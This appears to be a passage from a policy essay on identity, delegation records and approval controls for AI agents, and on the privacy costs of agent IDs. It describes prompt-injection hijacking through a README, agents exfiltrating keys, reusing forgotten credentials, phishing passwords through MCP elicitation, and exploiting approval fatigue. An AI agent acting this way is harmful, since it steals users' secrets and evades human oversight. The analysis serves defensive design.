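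A reader's comment on NIST's post points out that even when every identity is known and every authorisation is valid, people may be unable to tell whether the agent is still acting on the original intent. Narrower records reduce this problem, but any permission wide enough for useful work will also allow some misuse.

A mission would not automatically stop the upload either. Dana may have approved a mission to review the login code, but the hijacked agent can contact an ordinary website without consulting the person server, so the upload would be missing from the mission log. If an endpoint monitor recorded the connection, an analyst could compare the monitor's record with the mission log and ask why the agent had contacted a server that its approved work didn't require. Blocking unapproved outside connections would be better, because the keys would stay on the laptop.

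Delegation records also help only when something the agent needs requires one. In the Nx attack, no developer had approved the agents' search for sensitive files, but the files were on the developers' own machines, and operating systems open files without requiring a delegation record. A company's model gateway could require one by refusing any session without a task that the user had approved. The malware's agents would then have been unable to reach the model, unless they could use the approval of a session that was already running.

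An agent may also act without using its own record. NIST warns that agents can come across forgotten credentials and use them to get more access. Some agents in Lim and Neo's experiment did this with a colleague's credential. A service that accepted such a credential would attribute the agent's actions to the colleague.

### What narrow scopes and fresh approval can prevent

Narrow scopes can't stop all misuse, but they limit what a hijacked agent can reach. If Dana can open 40 repositories and gives the agent her own access token, malicious instructions in one repository's README put all 40 at risk, whereas with the one-hour record the attacker can reach only one.

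A permission expiry of an hour, or even ten minutes, will rarely interrupt the theft, because an agent can copy a typical repository in a minute or two. Short lifetimes are more useful against forgotten permissions and against an attacker who takes over the agent the following week.

Narrow scopes also turn some attacks into refused requests, which the company can record and investigate. But legitimate agents also hit tight limits, as Dana's did when it tried to save its fix. If 2 percent of a company's 10,000 daily agent sessions produce a refusal, a hijacked session that is refused will be one of about 200. The company would do better to focus on refusals that are hard to explain, such as a request for another team's production passwords.

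The company can require fresh approval for the riskiest steps, even if the agent already has general permission. Dana might let an agent edit code all afternoon but have to approve each public release of a package. This gives Dana, the only person who knows what she wanted, a chance to stop a hijacked agent before it does damage.

In Hardt's protocol, the agent can supply a justification for the access it wants, and Dana can question it before deciding. If an attacker controls the agent, however, the attacker may write both the justification and the answers, and a justification such as "Upload needed to verify the build" sounds reasonable. The protocol partly addresses this problem because, in some modes, the service itself issues a signed description of the access the agent needs. An approval screen should display that description more prominently than the agent's explanation.

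A hijacked agent might also try to get Dana's password. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common way to connect agents to tools, has a feature called elicitation for requesting more information from the user. MCP includes a warning against using elicitation for sensitive information, but NIST notes that it could still be used to request credentials. An agent with Dana's password could log in as Dana, and no service would require a delegation record.

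### Approval fatigue

People stop reading approval requests when they get too many, so asking for approval more often may not catch more misuse. NIST compares this to MFA bombing, in which an attacker with a stolen password sends repeated login notifications until the victim approves one to make them stop. An agent that asks too often can train its users to click "allow" even without an attacker. The comparison is convincing, though NIST has no measurements of this effect for agents.

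If an agent sends Dana 100 approval requests a day and she takes 20 seconds on each, she spends about 33 minutes a day on them. If one request in 5,000 is malicious, she will see one roughly every 50 working days, after approving thousands of harmless ones, and she is unlikely to still be reading carefully. Five requests a day would take her less than two minutes, and each would be unusual enough to deserve attention.

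Fatigue also weakens the records as evidence. If Dana approves every request, a log entry that reads "approved by Dana" says little about whether she wanted the action. An analyst would want to know how many requests she had received that day and how quickly she had answered this one.

One solution is to approve a plan instead of each step. NIST mentions "flight plans", which model providers are working on partly for this purpose, and Hardt's missions have a similar advantage. But a plan has to leave the agent some freedom, or the agent will soon need another approval. "Get this project to build" could cover hundreds of commands, including some an attacker would want to run. The best compromise is probably a fairly broad plan for work the company can easily undo, with separate approval for actions such as publishing software or sending data to a new destination.

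### Should every agent have an ID?

Some officials want agent identities to be as routine as identities for people and devices. PYMNTS's *US Intelligence Chief Calls for Digital IDs for AI Agents* (2026) reports remarks by Doug Cossa, chief information officer for the US intelligence community. Cossa said that after years of giving users and devices as little access as possible, security teams were now giving agents everything they need to work independently. He called for a common identity system, in effect a digital birth certificate for each agent. The government has no such system across its agencies, but Cossa's office planned to begin testing identity tools in the autumn.

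NIST's work is also at an early stage. In February, its cybersecurity centre published *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization* (NCCoE, 2026), which asked such basic questions as how a company might identify its agents. In October, NIST followed with *Design Tenets for Agent Identity Management Systems* (Booth, 2026). Design tenets can help a company decide what to build or buy, but they are not a protocol, so a monitor can use them only once somebody has built a system that follows them. The centre's own project page, *Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization*, still lists a draft project description as future work. ("SI" is the US government's current term for AI.)

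The main objection to universal agent IDs is that they may also identify the people behind the agents. Flanagan gives the example of someone who asks an agent to find a flight that suits a medical condition, stays under a certain price, and gets them to a job interview without their employer finding out. An airline's website could normally learn that this person was looking at flights, but a detailed delegation record could also reveal the medical condition, the budget and the interview. If the agent used the same identifier everywhere, companies could combine what they knew about the person.

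This is a serious objection, and better security doesn't answer it, because the companies receiving the information may be the ones that are supposed to have it. Flanagan responds by separating authority from identity. A service often needs to know that an agent has permission to do something, but not who gave the permission. The airline needs proof that the agent may spend $400, not the traveller's medical history, and it needs a name only when somebody buys a ticket.

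Hardt's protocol partly achieves this. It hides the agent's identifier from the service in three of the five access modes, and each of the person's tokens is made for a single service. But whoever runs the person server still holds a very revealing history of where the agent goes and what the person asked for. People can choose their own person server, but an employee using a company's agent would presumably have to accept the employer's.

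Inside a company, the objection is weaker for basic records. Dana's employer already knows that she works on the login code, and learns little more from a record that her agent may read it for an hour. Mission descriptions and questions are more sensitive, for much the same reasons that stored prompts are. The intelligence agencies could likewise require IDs for their own agents without requiring them for everyone who sends an agent to book a flight.

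Privacy does make defence harder. In the SesameOp case, one API key linked all the infected computers, so OpenAI could cut them off together. If every service receives a different identifier for the same agent, two services can't compare records to discover that one hijacked agent is attacking both. Someone would have to ask the person server, which would need rules about who may ask and what evidence they must provide.
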